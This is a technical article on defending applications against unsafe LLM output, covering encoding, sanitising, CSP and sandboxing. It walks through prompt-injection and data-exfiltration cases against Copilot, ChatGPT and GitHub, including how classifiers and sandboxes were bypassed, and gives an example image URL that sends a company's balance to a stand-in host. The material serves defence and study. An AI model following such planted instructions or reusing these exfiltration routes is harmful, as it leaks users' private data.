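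But a record that lists only CWE-116 does not show that a model was involved. MITRE's example of CWE-1426 avoids this by linking two CWE numbers. In it, a graphical interface for ChatGPT checks what the user types but not what the model returns (CWE-1426), which results in XSS (CWE-79). A CVE record can hold more than one CWE number, so analysts could record both the type of injection and the involvement of a model, though MITRE does not advise them to.

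### The records under CWE-1426 and CWE-1427

GCVE, a European vulnerability database, lists only three CVE records under CWE-1426 on its page *Improper Validation of Generative AI Output*. Mattermost, a maker of team chat software, filed two of them, and Microsoft filed the third for GitHub Copilot and the code editor Visual Studio Code. All three date from after MITRE's CWE version 4.17, so both companies used a number that MITRE had already discouraged.

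The CWE catalogue has a separate entry, CWE-1427, for flaws in how an application builds its prompts. GCVE's *Improper Neutralization of Input Used for LLM Prompting* lists 19 records under CWE-1427 up to mid-October 2026. MITRE allows the entry to be used for real vulnerabilities, although the notes for CWE-1426 still place most prompt injection under CWE-77. The table compares the three records under CWE-1426 with three of the 19 under CWE-1427. Severity is on the industry's standard scale from 0 to 10.

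| Record | Product | Filed under | Flaw | Severity |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CVE-2025-31363 | Mattermost | CWE-1426 | The application does not limit which domains the model can contact, so an attacker can use prompt injection to extract data | 3.0 |
| CVE-2025-55074 | Mattermost | CWE-1426 | A missing permission check lets users find out when others have read a channel | 3.0 |
| CVE-2025-62453 | GitHub Copilot and Visual Studio Code | CWE-1426 and CWE-693 | An attacker can bypass an unnamed security feature | 5.0 |
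| CVE-2026-96893 | GitLab | CWE-1427 | A user can insert content into an agent's instructions, and commands may run under other users' names | 7.3 |
| CVE-2026-78379 | Amazon Strands Agents Tools | CWE-1427 | A crafted prompt can bypass human approval before Python code runs | 8.1 |
| CVE-2026-77931 | MoviePilot | CWE-1427 | Instructions in web pages can lead the model to run shell commands | 8.8 |

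Of the three records under CWE-1426, only Mattermost's missing limit on domains clearly fits the definition. Another record covers a flaw that reveals when people read a channel, which is a permissions problem, and its description doesn't mention model output. Microsoft's description mostly repeats the title of the CWE entry, so a reader can't tell which output went unchecked. MITRE's own example, the ChatGPT interface with XSS, isn't among the three. According to the records, none of the three flaws was known to have been exploited at the time of assessment.

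Some of the more serious output handling flaws are in the other group. MoviePilot, an open-source program, had a list of forbidden shell commands, but the model could get past it by setting an option that confirmed a dangerous command. Amazon's tool normally asked a person to confirm before it ran Python, but a prompt could make another tool pass along a setting that turned the confirmation off. In both products, the setting that controlled the safety check was part of the model's output. The application has to choose that setting in code that the model can't influence, because rewording the prompt wouldn't reliably fix the flaw.

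The totals of three and 19 are therefore a poor guide to how common each flaw is. They may also come from different dates, because the newest change on the page for CWE-1426 is from February 2026. OWASP sorted 6,639 incidents, so even if its data included all 22 of these records, it must have classified nearly everything else without using these two CWE numbers. To find out how often applications mishandle model output, a researcher would have to read records filed under XSS, command injection, code injection, encoding errors and CWE-1427, and check whether the descriptions mention a model. This search would still miss every record whose author didn't mention one.

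### Turning the guidance into tests

Several of OWASP's recommendations are especially useful to developers because someone can check whether an application follows them. To check encoding, a tester can replace the model with a function that always returns the same reply, such as a word in bold tags. If the browser shows the tags as text, the application has encoded them. The tester can also have the function return the surname O'Reilly to check that the database stores the apostrophe correctly, and read the code to confirm that queries use parameters.

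Replacing the model with a fixed reply is important in testing because models don't reliably produce the same reply twice. To detect the weakness, MITRE suggests adapting known prompt injection attacks to the product and seeing what happens, ideally together with a design review. Such attacks show whether the complete system can be exploited. But if the model refuses to write a script tag, the tester doesn't learn what the page would do with one, and the next version of the model may write one. A fixed reply tests the application separately from the model.

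Other recommendations need more detail before anyone can test them. "Treat the model as any other user" doesn't specify which user, or which functions that user may call. A tester can confirm that a page has a CSP, but not that it is "strict" until someone defines the term. Similarly, a tester can check that the application logs every reply, but not that it detects "unusual patterns" in those logs until the company decides what is usual.

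ASVS can provide some of the missing detail. Respan describes it as a long list of specific controls to verify, whereas the top ten lists risks to be aware of. For example, ASVS has testers verify that database queries use parameters or have equivalent protection, rather than telling developers to avoid injection. Its requirements apply to untrusted data in general, so a tester only has to add the model to the list of sources of such data. However, OWASP's entry links to an outdated version of ASVS, citing chapter 5 of version 4, on validation, sanitisation and encoding. Version 5.0, released in May 2025, covers these subjects in its first two chapters and uses chapter 5 for file handling, so a developer who looks up chapter 5 there will find the wrong requirements.

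Of MITRE's mitigations, only running the component in a non-privileged space is easy to test. A tester can make the component try to read a forbidden file and see whether it succeeds. A company that rents its model from a supplier has little control over the training examples. How easily a guardrail can be tested depends on the rules it applies, and MITRE doesn't specify any.

The advice on semantic comparators is the vaguest. MITRE doesn't explain what the application should compare the output with, or how similar two texts must be before it acts. A comparator might recognise a reworded version of a forbidden statement, which would help with a content policy, but it is a poor choice for protecting a sink. A delivery note means practically the same thing with or without a hidden script tag, so a comparator could miss the tag and let the script run in the browser.

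### Official texts that repeat the advice

Some public authorities have adopted OWASP's advice, with changes. The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre recommends validation, encoding to suit the sink, and logging, much as OWASP does. It also fills two of the gaps in OWASP's seven recommendations by advising developers to give the application as few privileges as possible and to use strict query builders, which assemble a query from approved parts, instead of running model-written SQL directly. For shells and functions such as `eval`, it is stricter than OWASP and tells developers never to execute model output automatically. That rule is clear and testable, but under it the office assistant would have to ask the employee to approve each Python program it writes to add up invoices.

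Australia's government appears to go further by requiring developers of language model applications to mitigate the whole OWASP top ten. *[ISM] LLM risk mitigation (OWASP top 10)*, an unofficial compilation of security controls, quotes this requirement from a control labelled ISM, the usual abbreviation for Australia's Information Security Manual. As quoted, the control doesn't specify an edition, so it is unclear whether an application that met it in July 2026 had to start dealing with terminals and auto-fetched images in August. It also doesn't define mitigation, so assessors have to choose the tests.

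## Displaying model text safely in web pages

OWASP advises developers to choose an encoding that suits the sink. This can be difficult in a browser because a single web page can combine HTML, JavaScript, CSS and URLs, each with its own special characters. The same text can therefore be safe in one part of a page and dangerous in another.

### One string in four places

Suppose the office assistant finds a supplier recorded as `<b>O'Reilly & "Sons"</b>` because somebody pasted the name in with its bold tags. The application should display exactly those characters. The table shows how it must write them in four places.

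| Place in the page | How the application writes the string |
|---|---|
| Body text, between two tags | `&lt;b&gt;O'Reilly &amp; "Sons"&lt;/b&gt;` |
| Attribute in double quotation marks | `&lt;b&gt;O'Reilly &amp; &quot;Sons&quot;&lt;/b&gt;` |
| JavaScript string in a script block | `\u003Cb\u003EO\u0027Reilly \u0026 \u0022Sons\u0022\u003C/b\u003E` |
| Value in a web address | `%3Cb%3EO%27Reilly%20%26%20%22Sons%22%3C%2Fb%3E` |

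In body text, the browser reads `<` as the start of a tag and `&` as the start of a code for a special character, so the application replaces them with `&lt;` and `&amp;`. It has to replace `&` first. Otherwise, it would turn the `&lt;` it had just written into `&amp;lt;`, and the reader would see `&lt;` on the page. Quotation marks have no special meaning in body text and can stay. OWASP's *Cross Site Scripting Prevention Cheat Sheet* recommends encoding them too, so that the same function also works for attributes.

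An attribute is a named setting inside a tag, such as the `title` that appears when the mouse rests on a word. Its value ends at the next matching quotation mark. The body-text version would end the value just before "Sons", and the browser would read the rest as further attributes. This example would only garble the tag, but hostile text could add an attribute that runs a script in the same way.

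The browser doesn't decode HTML codes in a script block, so a program given text encoded for an HTML attribute could display `&lt;b&gt;` to the reader. HTML encoding also leaves backslashes unchanged, but in JavaScript a backslash changes the meaning of the next character. If a reply ends with a folder path such as `C:\Invoices\`, the last backslash makes the closing quotation mark part of the string, which then continues into the code after it. JavaScript escaping fails in an HTML attribute because the backslash has no special meaning there, so a quotation mark written as `\"` still ends the attribute.

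In a web address, `&` separates one parameter from the next, so a search link containing a supplier name with an `&` would search only for the part before it. HTML encoding doesn't prevent this, because the browser decodes `&amp;` back into `&` before it uses the address. Percent encoding keeps the name intact. Because an address in a link also sits inside an attribute, OWASP tells developers to percent-encode the value first and then encode the whole address for the attribute.

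Encoding can't make an address safe if the model supplies all of it. An address that starts with `javascript:` runs code when someone clicks on it, and it may contain no characters that need encoding. The application has to check the scheme (the part before the colon) against an allow-list such as `http` and `https`.

Some HTML attributes, such as `onclick`, hold JavaScript. The browser decodes HTML-encoded characters in these attributes before running the code, so an encoded apostrophe becomes an ordinary apostrophe again. OWASP recommends keeping untrusted code out of such attributes. It also lists places where no encoding is enough, including tag names and script code outside a string.

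Chat applications often build their pages with JavaScript in the browser. The program can then assign a reply to an element's `textContent` property, which is simpler than encoding it because the browser stores the reply as text without parsing it. If the program uses `innerHTML` instead, the browser parses the reply as HTML. *Trusting AI Output?*, by the login software company Auth0, recommends switching from `innerHTML` to `textContent` in a chatbot that summarises web pages.

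The advice is sound, but Auth0 is wrong that the browser would run a script tag inserted through `innerHTML`. Other markup inserted the same way can run code, so a developer who tests a page with a script tag and sees nothing happen could wrongly conclude that the page is safe.

### Templates that choose the encoding

Programmers who choose an encoding by hand for every value make mistakes. *SCRIPTGARD* (Saxena, Molnar and Livshits, 2011) examines a web application with over 400,000 lines of code. The errors it describes occurred because programmers used encoding and filtering functions in the wrong context or combined them inconsistently, not because the functions were faulty.

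In the same year, Samuel, Saxena and Song automated the choice in *Context-Sensitive Auto-Sanitization in Web Templating Languages Using Type Qualifiers*. Their system works on templates, which are pages with gaps that an application fills in for each visitor. The system trusts the fixed parts of a template because the developer wrote them. When it compiles the template, before any gaps are filled, it uses those parts to work out the context of each gap and inserts the matching function.

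The context in which a value appears can depend on which path the program takes. Samuel and colleagues give the example of a template that displays a contact's picture. If the contact has a name, the picture link becomes a parameter near the end of an address and should be percent-encoded. If there is no name, the link is the whole address, and the system has to check its scheme. Samuel and colleagues label each value with a type qualifier, which records the contexts in which it is safe, and follow these labels along every path. Only a small fraction of cases have to be decided when the page runs.

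In a test on 1,035 existing templates written for Google Closure Templates, a framework used in Gmail and Google Docs, the system required no changes to the templates. It added 3% to 9.6% to the running time of demanding benchmarks, compared with 78% to 510% for a method that parses all output as the program runs. The guarantee covers only the template, so if other code inserts the finished HTML into a script, the encoding is no longer correct.

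*Package template* documents a similar system included with the Go programming language. The system treats the template's author as trusted and encodes the data to suit each context. That assumption fails if an application lets a model write the template as well as the data, because the system then treats the model's markup as the developer's own.

### Turning Markdown into HTML

Chat replies contain headings, tables and code samples, so a chat application can't just HTML-encode everything. If it converts the Markdown to HTML and then encodes the result, the reader sees `<h2>` instead of a heading. If it encodes the Markdown first, it damages notation such as the `>` that marks a quotation. Dangerous links would also still get through, because Markdown writes links with brackets and parentheses, which HTML encoding doesn't change.

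A safer procedure has four steps:

1. Parse the Markdown into headings, paragraphs, links and so on, treating any HTML in it as plain text.
2. Render these parts as HTML, encoding the text and checking the scheme of every address.
3. Sanitise the resulting HTML with an allow-list of tags and attributes.
4. Insert the sanitised HTML into the page without changing it further.

The third step backs up the first two by catching mistakes in the converter and its plug-ins. OWASP recommends the DOMPurify library for this step and tells developers to update such libraries regularly because people keep finding ways around them.

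Sanitising Markdown before converting it to HTML gives little protection. A Markdown link to a `javascript:` address contains no HTML tags, so an HTML sanitiser treats it as ordinary text and leaves it unchanged. The converter then turns it into a working link.

Markdown allows raw HTML, and some converters copy it straight into their output. A script tag in the supplier's delivery note would pass through such a converter unchanged. React, a library for building web pages, encodes text by default, and version 19 also blocks `javascript:` addresses in links. But an application that converts Markdown into a string of HTML has to bypass the default encoding to display it, using React's `dangerouslySetInnerHTML` property. Building the page elements directly from the parsed Markdown avoids the need for this bypass.

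Changes made after sanitising can undo it. If an application cleans a reply and then colours its code samples or adds links to its sources, a fault in either feature could put unsafe markup back. These features should run before the sanitising.

Reopened and shared replies need the same treatment as new ones. Fast Feed's *CHATGPT*, a short news summary, describes CVE-2025-43714, a flaw in which ChatGPT rendered tags inside code blocks when someone reopened a chat or shared it through a link. An attacker could use the flaw to show misleading messages or embed malicious addresses, and OpenAI has since patched it. A product can avoid this kind of flaw by using the same rendering code for live, reopened and shared replies.

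Sanitising doesn't help when the harmful part is the message itself. Permiso, a security company, planted instructions in a GitHub project's description and had ChatGPT summarise the page. ChatGPT produced a real summary followed by a fake security notice, with a link that appeared to come from OpenAI. A sanitiser would have kept the notice, since it used only permitted formatting. An application can make such deception harder by showing where links lead and displaying its own notices outside the reply.

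### Replies that arrive in pieces

Most chat products display a reply while the model is still generating it. The text arrives a few characters at a time, so a tag or link can be split between two pieces. If the application sanitises each piece separately, `<scr` and `ipt>` may both pass as harmless text and then form a tag when the application joins them.

The application can also make the reverse mistake. A reply about web design may include a code sample containing tags that the application should show as text, but a parser that receives only the latest piece of the reply can't detect that the code sample began in an earlier piece.

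The simplest safe method is to keep all the Markdown received so far and repeat all four steps whenever a new piece arrives. This gets slow because a reply in *n* equal pieces requires processing 1 + 2 + … + *n* = *n*(*n* + 1)/2 pieces in total, which is 500,500 for a reply of 1,000 pieces. Updating the display only a few times a second reduces the work considerably.

An application can also keep finished paragraphs and reprocess only the last one. This needs some care because Markdown allows a link's address to appear at the end of a document, far from the link. The application can display an unfinished link as plain text until its address arrives and passes the scheme check.

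### When sanitising fails

A Content Security Policy (CSP) can stop a script that gets past the sanitiser. The server sends the policy along with the page, and the browser enforces it. A short one might read:

```
Content-Security-Policy: script-src 'nonce-7Qf2xL'; connect-src 'self'; img-src 'self'
```

The first rule allows only scripts marked with the nonce `7Qf2xL`, a code the server puts on its own scripts, so a script tag left in a reply by mistake won't run. The other two rules restrict data requests and images to the page's own site, which limits how images can be used to send data out.

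A nonce works only if the server picks a new, unpredictable one for each page. Imperva's *XSS Marks the Spot* describes an older flaw in ChatGPT, where the nonce never changed. A researcher uploaded an HTML file containing a script and opened it through a citation in ChatGPT's answer. The CSP blocked the script at first, but it ran after the researcher added the fixed nonce to the script tag.

OWASP advises against relying on a Content Security Policy (CSP) as the main defence because it is easy to set up wrongly. A policy that only restricts scripts also does not stop model output from displaying a fake notice or a misleading link.

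Trusted Types, a related browser feature, guards against developers forgetting to sanitise text. A developer turns it on by adding `require-trusted-types-for 'script'` to the CSP. In browsers that support it, `innerHTML` and similar sinks then reject ordinary strings and accept only values that have passed through a function the developer has approved, which can call DOMPurify. If a programmer later assigns a model's reply directly to `innerHTML`, the browser reports an error instead of parsing it.

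OWASP counts Trusted Types among the few controls that eliminate whole classes of XSS. The protection still depends on the approved function, because the browser doesn't check whether the function removes anything.

### Generated pages that must run scripts

Suppose the employee asks the office assistant for a spending chart with a slider for the month. The slider needs a script, so the application has to run it where it can't do any harm.

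Browsers normally let a script read pages and stored data only from its own origin, which is the combination of a page's scheme, host name and port. If the company serves generated pages from a separate domain, scripts in those pages can't read the assistant's page or use its stored data.

The application displays the generated page in a frame, a window embedded in the main page. With the `sandbox` attribute, the browser blocks scripts, forms and popups in the frame and gives its content a separate origin. The developer can restore permissions one at a time, such as the permission to run scripts, which a chart needs. Restoring the generated page's normal origin as well would be dangerous if the page came from the assistant's domain, because its script could then reach the main page and remove the sandbox.

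A sandboxed script can still contact other servers, so the preview needs its own CSP to restrict network requests. The script can also send messages to the main page through the browser function `postMessage`, for example to report the chart's height. The main page should check which frame sent each message and reject unexpected values, such as HTML where it expects a number for the height.

*Do the Math* (Goyal, 2026) shows what can happen without these checks. Mukul Goyal and colleagues at the security company Parameter examined ChatGPT's Preview feature, which turns HTML from a conversation into a working page. ChatGPT ran the page in a restricted frame on a separate address, and the code inside couldn't read the main page.

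The same conversation contained an interactive graph, which loaded a mathematics library called MathLive into ChatGPT's main page. MathLive accepted messages about its on-screen keyboard from any sender. A message could include HTML for the keyboard's layout, so the preview could send HTML that MathLive inserted into the main page.

Two further safeguards failed to stop the attack. The HTML passed through a function called `createHTML`, the name Trusted Types uses for this kind of approved function, but the function marked the text as trusted without cleaning it. The inserted HTML created a new unsandboxed frame, which the browser treated as part of chatgpt.com. ChatGPT's CSP blocked scripts written directly in that frame but allowed scripts from YouTube, and the researchers found a YouTube service that would return code they chose.

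The code ran with the access of whoever had opened the shared conversation. In tests between separate accounts, it listed private chats, opened one and sent part of it to an outside server. According to The Hacker News' *A Shared ChatGPT Link Could Run Attacker Code in Your Session* (2026), Parameter reported the flaw on 18 October and did not report any real-world use. By 26 October, ChatGPT rejected the messages the attack relied on. OpenAI gave the flaw its highest severity rating and paid a $5,000 bounty, which Willison (2026) called "a bit cheap" in *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts*.

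Rejecting the messages was a better fix than removing YouTube from the CSP would have been. As The Hacker News points out, blocking YouTube alone would still have let the preview insert HTML into the main page. An attacker could then have looked for another permitted site with a similar service, or used HTML that needs no script.

### The preview that undid Lockdown Mode

A different flaw in the same preview feature affected users of Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting that gives extra protection to people who work with sensitive information. OpenAI launched it for enterprise customers in February 2026 and extended it to personal accounts in June, according to *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026). Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, quotes the company's explanation that the mode targets the last stage of data theft by limiting outgoing network requests.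 The mode doesn't keep prompt injections out of the material that ChatGPT reads.

ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode limits web browsing to cached pages, blocks images from the internet, and turns off file downloads and several features that connect to outside services, according to *Check Point Bypassed ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode With a Popup* (Duggan, 2026). HTML previews remained available. They ran in two nested sandboxed frames, and ChatGPT asked the user for approval before a preview could load anything from outside.

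The security company Check Point found a way around the popup check in ChatGPT's preview. The preview's sandbox let popups open without its restrictions, so ChatGPT replaced the browser's function for opening windows with a version that required the user's approval. But a preview could create a frame inside itself, and the browser gave that frame a fresh copy of the original function. A window opened from that frame was outside both the sandbox and Lockdown Mode.

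The consequences depended on the program that displayed the preview. In the ChatGPT Classic desktop app, the popup could open without a click. An attacker could publish a custom version of ChatGPT that sent the whole conversation to an outside server while the user chatted with it. The popup also kept the ChatGPT icon, and the attacker controlled its title and contents, so it could pass for an official update or login page.

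OpenAI told Check Point on 18 September that it had removed both popup permissions from the outer frame. Check Point confirmed by testing that the technique no longer worked, and Duggan found no evidence that anyone had exploited the flaw. The new restriction is stronger because the browser enforces it on every frame inside the outer one. The earlier protection was only a modified JavaScript function running alongside the untrusted code, which could obtain an unmodified copy.

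OpenAI had warned that Lockdown Mode might not stop every leak, saying that risk could remain through "unforeseen combinations of capabilities" (The Next Web, *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft*). Check Point told The Hacker News that its finding and Parameter's were different vulnerabilities in the same component (*Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction*, 2026). In both cases, the preview's code couldn't read the main page directly, but it could still affect something outside its frame.

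Isolation therefore has to cover messages, network requests, new windows and nested frames in every program that displays previews. A developer can check much of this with a fixed test page that tries to read the main page, contact an outside server and open a window, first directly and then from a frame inside itself. The developer should run it in both the browser and the desktop app, with any stricter mode turned on. The test page would probably have exposed the popup flaw, but it would have missed the MathLive flaw unless its author knew the library's message format. Someone therefore also has to list every message listener in the main page and check which senders each one accepts. That list can change whenever the product adds a feature, even one unrelated to previews, such as a graph.

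## Links and images that carry data out

Encoding and sanitising stop a browser from running a model's text as code, but the browser can still send a request, and the address in that request can carry private text to the recipient.

Say a supplier's email tells the office assistant to end each answer with the supplier's logo and to add the company's unpaid balance to the logo's address. The reply then contains an image at this address:

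```
https://images.supplier.example/logo.png?balance=40000
```

This address uses `https`, has no characters that need encoding and is in an ordinary image tag, which a typical sanitiser keeps. When the browser displays the reply, it requests the image from the supplier's server, which records the whole address, including the balance, in its log. This happens whether the server returns a logo, a transparent dot or an error message.

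Marketers use the same mechanism to find out who has opened their emails. The sender chooses the image's address before sending the email, so a request for it reveals little more than that somebody opened the message. But an assistant writes the address after reading the mailbox, so it can include anything it found there. Browsers and servers generally accept addresses of at least 2,000 characters, enough for about 300 words.

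### Four ways to trigger a request

Images are the best-known route, but an assistant's output can cause a request in other ways too.

| Channel | What triggers the request | What usually sends it |
|---|---|---|
| Image in a reply | The application displays the reply | The user's browser |
| Link in a reply | The user clicks | The user's browser |
| Link preview | Someone posts or saves text containing the link | The chat or file service's server |
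| Page the assistant reads | The model asks for the page | The assistant's server |

A link is the weakest channel for an attacker because somebody has to click it, but it is hard to block because an assistant that can't link to outside websites is much less useful. Link previews, the small boxes with a title and picture that chat programs show under a link, work without a click. If the office assistant posts its answer in a team chat, the chat service may fetch every link in the message before anyone reads it.

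The last column determines which defences can work. A Content Security Policy (CSP) works only in the browser, so it has no effect on requests that a server sends. Its rule for images also doesn't cover links that the user clicks.

### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot is a real product similar to the imaginary office assistant. It answers employees' questions using their mailboxes, files and Teams chats. Researchers have repeatedly extracted data from it since 2025, and the table lists the main attacks.

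| Attack | What the employee had to do | How the data left | Repaired |
|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711) | Ask a question that made Copilot retrieve the attacker's email | Image, relayed by Teams | May 2025 |
| SearchLeak (CVE-2026-42824) | Click a link to a Microsoft website | Image, relayed by Bing | By mid-June 2026 |
| ReLeak, images (CVE-2026-124115) | Ask a question that made Copilot retrieve the attacker's email | Image, relayed by Bing | 15 November 2026 |
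| ReLeak, files (CVE-2026-124132) | The same | Link in a generated file, fetched by Microsoft's servers | 11 November 2026 |
| ReLeak, code (CVE-2026-78501) | The same | Program that Copilot ran | 17 September 2026 |

Aim Labs, the research team at Aim Security, reported EchoLeak to Microsoft in January 2025, according to Willison (2025). Information Security Buzz reports that Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May, so customers had nothing to install. When the flaw became public on 11 June, Fortune (2025) called it the first known "zero-click" attack on an AI agent, meaning one that works without the victim clicking anything or even opening the message.

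In the EchoLeak attack on Copilot, the attacker only had to send an employee an email. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) explains that Copilot retrieves emails related to the employee's question, so the researchers wrote a long email with sections on everyday subjects such as onboarding and leave. Each section repeated the same instructions, which told the reader to put the most sensitive information available into a web address. The email got past all four of the controls that were meant to stop such an attack.

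Microsoft's injection classifier should have kept the email away from the model. The researchers phrased the instructions as if they were for the employee and never mentioned Copilot or AI, and the classifier let the message through.

Copilot also removed outside links and images from its replies, but it recognised only the usual Markdown notation, in which the address comes directly after the link's text. Markdown also lets an author put the address on a separate line and refer to it by a label. Copilot left these addresses in place, and the browser displayed them as working links and images. An application can avoid this mistake by checking addresses after it parses the Markdown, because parsing turns both notations into the same kind of object.

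The CSP did better, blocking images from the attacker's own server. But it allowed images from 29 other addresses and groups of addresses, most of them Microsoft's, and Ravia's team searched these for a service that would forward a request.

A browser also checks the target of a redirect against the CSP, so the researchers needed a server that would contact the attacker directly. They found one in SharePoint, Microsoft's file-sharing product, but it worked only if the employee had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. A Teams service worked without an invitation. The browser asked Teams for an image, which the CSP allowed, and Teams fetched the address in the request. The second request never went through the browser, so the CSP couldn't stop it.

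The remaining control was that Copilot usually cites the sources of its answers, which might have made the employee suspicious. But the email included an instruction that, for compliance reasons, nobody should refer to it, so Copilot did not cite it.

*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) likewise describes the attack as a chain of bypasses. The bypassed layers weren't equally valuable, so the attack doesn't show that Microsoft simply needed more of them. A complete check on addresses would have stopped both the images and the links. Closing the Teams relay would have stopped the zero-click version but left links for the employee to click. A better classifier would have made the attacker try another wording.

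Ravia traces the root of the problem to an earlier step, which the article calls an LLM scope violation, where instructions from an untrusted source make the model use trusted data without the user's consent. This supports blocking actions based on where the data came from. The Teams relay is still just as much a fault, because an attacker who had fooled Copilot in some other way could have used it too.

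### SearchLeak

A year later, the security company Varonis got data out through a different Microsoft service. Its *SearchLeak* (2026), published on 15 June, describes an attack that needed one click. Copilot's search page accepted a query in its web address and treated the query as instructions to the model. An attacker could therefore write a link to a genuine Microsoft website that made Copilot search the employee's mailbox as soon as the page opened.

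The instructions told Copilot to put an email's subject line into the address of an image. A subject line alone can be sensitive because companies often put login codes there, and the one stolen in the demonstration contained a security code.

Copilot tried to block unwanted HTML by wrapping each finished reply in a code block, so that the browser would show any tags as text. However, the page displayed the reply as HTML while the model was still writing it, so the browser requested the image before the code block was added. Varonis advises developers to sanitise output as it is displayed, not in a later step.

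The CSP should still have blocked the request, but it allowed images from Bing, whose search-by-image feature has Bing's servers fetch a picture from any address the user supplies. The browser sent its request to Bing, and Bing then contacted the attacker's server with the email's title in the address. This kind of flaw is called server-side request forgery, because an outsider chooses where a company's server sends a request.

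Microsoft rated the flaw critical and fixed it on its servers. According to ThaiCERT's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click*, the company classed it as command injection, which fits MITRE's advice on prompt injection but doesn't show that Bing was involved. The list of policy entries that Ravia published in 2025 already included `bing.com` and all its subdomains, so anyone reviewing it after EchoLeak for services that fetch addresses could have found the route.

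### ReLeak

Cato Networks bought Aim Security in September 2025, and Aim's researchers became Cato AI Labs. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), published on 3 December, reports the team's three new zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot. All three began as EchoLeak did, with an unopened email that Copilot retrieved while answering an ordinary question, and Microsoft's classifier failed again. According to Punto Informatico's *ReLeak*, Copilot didn't follow blunt commands but could still follow instructions that looked like legitimate requests.

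In the first attack, Copilot put confidential text into the address of an image, and Bing passed the request on. Antipov (2026), in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, notes that this resembled SearchLeak, except that the employee no longer had to click. Cato sent its reports to Microsoft between 29 July and 20 August, so Bing was still relaying requests more than a month after Varonis publicly explained the problem. Either the earlier fix did not change Bing's fetching, or the researchers found another way to trigger it. Microsoft closed the route on 15 November.

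In the second attack, the email made Copilot create a file containing a link with confidential data in the address. Copilot can save Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files to a company's online storage, and Microsoft's servers fetched the link while processing the new file in the background. In Cato's tests this happened one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, whether or not anybody opened the file. A filter on Copilot's replies would have missed the link because it was only in the file, and a CSP would not have blocked the request because no browser made it. Either the application has to check addresses in the files it creates, or the background process must not fetch outside links.

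The third route was Copilot's Python sandbox. According to Microsoft's documentation, the sandbox allowed no network traffic in either direction, but the researchers got around the restriction and sent data directly to an outside server. The sandbox's network limits should have blocked this regardless of what code the model wrote. The flaw's severity score was raised from 7.4 to 8.6 out of 10.

Microsoft fixed the sandbox first, on 17 September, between four and just over seven weeks after Cato's report. The flaws involving files and images each took at least 83 days to fix. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) quotes the researchers' complaint that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. That seems fair for the classifier and Bing, but it is a little harsh overall, because two of the three routes depended on features that turn Copilot's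 output into files and programs, and EchoLeak had used neither.

Finding such routes has also become easier. Antipov reports that Cato's researchers had AI agents write test cases, study Copilot's refusals and adjust the next attempt. An attacker could automate the search in the same way.

### A permitted domain that passes requests on

Teams and Bing failed in the same way. A domain allow-list works only if data sent to a permitted domain stays with the domain's owner. If any service on the domain fetches addresses that visitors supply, a visitor can use it to reach the whole internet. The background process in ReLeak provided a similar route without being on any allow-list, because Microsoft's own servers sent the request.

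The fault is easy to overlook because it comes from combining two reasonable behaviours. A search engine has to fetch a picture to search with it, and Copilot may well need to show pictures from Bing. The people who maintain Bing had no particular reason to think of their image search as part of Copilot's defences.

Wildcards make such combinations more likely. Eleven of the 29 entries in Copilot's policy covered every subdomain of a domain, including `sharepoint.com`, where any Microsoft customer can have a site. In the SharePoint version of EchoLeak, the image's address was on the attacker's subdomain, which the policy allowed just as it allowed the victim's. Varonis recommends reviewing each permitted domain for services that fetch addresses supplied by users. A reviewer should also check whether outsiders can host anything on the domain or see its traffic, for example through visitor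 statistics.

### Whether anyone has used these attacks

There is no public evidence that criminals or spies have used any of the Copilot attacks. According to Ravia, Microsoft confirmed that EchoLeak affected no customers. ThaiCERT knew of no active use of SearchLeak, and Cato knew of no victims of ReLeak when it published its findings.

This is only partly reassuring, because most of these attacks would have been hard to detect. The employee would have noticed nothing, and a company watching its own network would have seen only a browser contacting Bing or Teams, which is routine. Microsoft could search the logs of the relaying services, so its statement about EchoLeak is stronger evidence than a researcher's remark that no victims have come forward, though Microsoft also has an interest in the answer. The attacks were practical and required few resources, but it remains uncertain whether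 anyone tried them before the flaws were fixed.

### Blocking images and limiting domains

The simplest defence is to show no images from outside addresses. This closes the image channel completely, provided that the application removes images after parsing rather than searching the text for one notation, as Copilot did. Many assistants would lose little, because a chart that the application draws itself can be part of the page or come from the company's own server at an address the model didn't write. But a shopping assistant is not much use without product photographs. The defence also does nothing about links, previews or files, so it would have stopped only one of the three ReLeak attacks.

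A domain allow-list lets the application keep showing some images, but an allowed domain could relay data to an outsider. The safest domain to allow is one whose server stores fixed image files, fetches nothing and lets no outsider read its logs. Where it can, the application should compare the whole address with a list of known image addresses. If it checks only the domain, the model can still write 2,000 characters of its own after the domain name, and the company depends on every service at that domain to ignore them.

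CSP enforces the list in the browser, which helps when the application's own check has a gap. In EchoLeak, the policy stopped the direct request that Copilot's filter had missed, so the researchers had to look for a relay. A CSP can limit images to a particular folder on a server, but unlike an application, it can't check the part of an address after the question mark, where the supplier's logo carried the balance.

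An image proxy is a server that fetches images on the browser's behalf. Websites use proxies to hide visitors' network addresses from the owners of outside images. A proxy that accepts any image URL hides the visitor's network address but still passes on the stolen text, which is the same fault as in Teams and Bing. A stricter proxy accepts only URLs that carry a digital signature from the application. The model can't produce a valid signature, so the proxy rejects any URL the model writes to carry private text.

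GitHub had a proxy of this kind, called Camo, and in 2025 the security company Legit Security got around it with an attack called CamoLeak. The researchers hid instructions in a proposed code change. When a developer asked GitHub Copilot Chat about the change, the assistant could read whatever the developer could, including private code. The researchers had already obtained a valid signed address for each letter and symbol, all leading to invisible images on their own server. Copilot Chat could therefore reveal a secret without writing a new address, by displaying the images in the order that spelled it out while the server recorded the sequence of requests. GitHub responded by turning off images in Copilot Chat.

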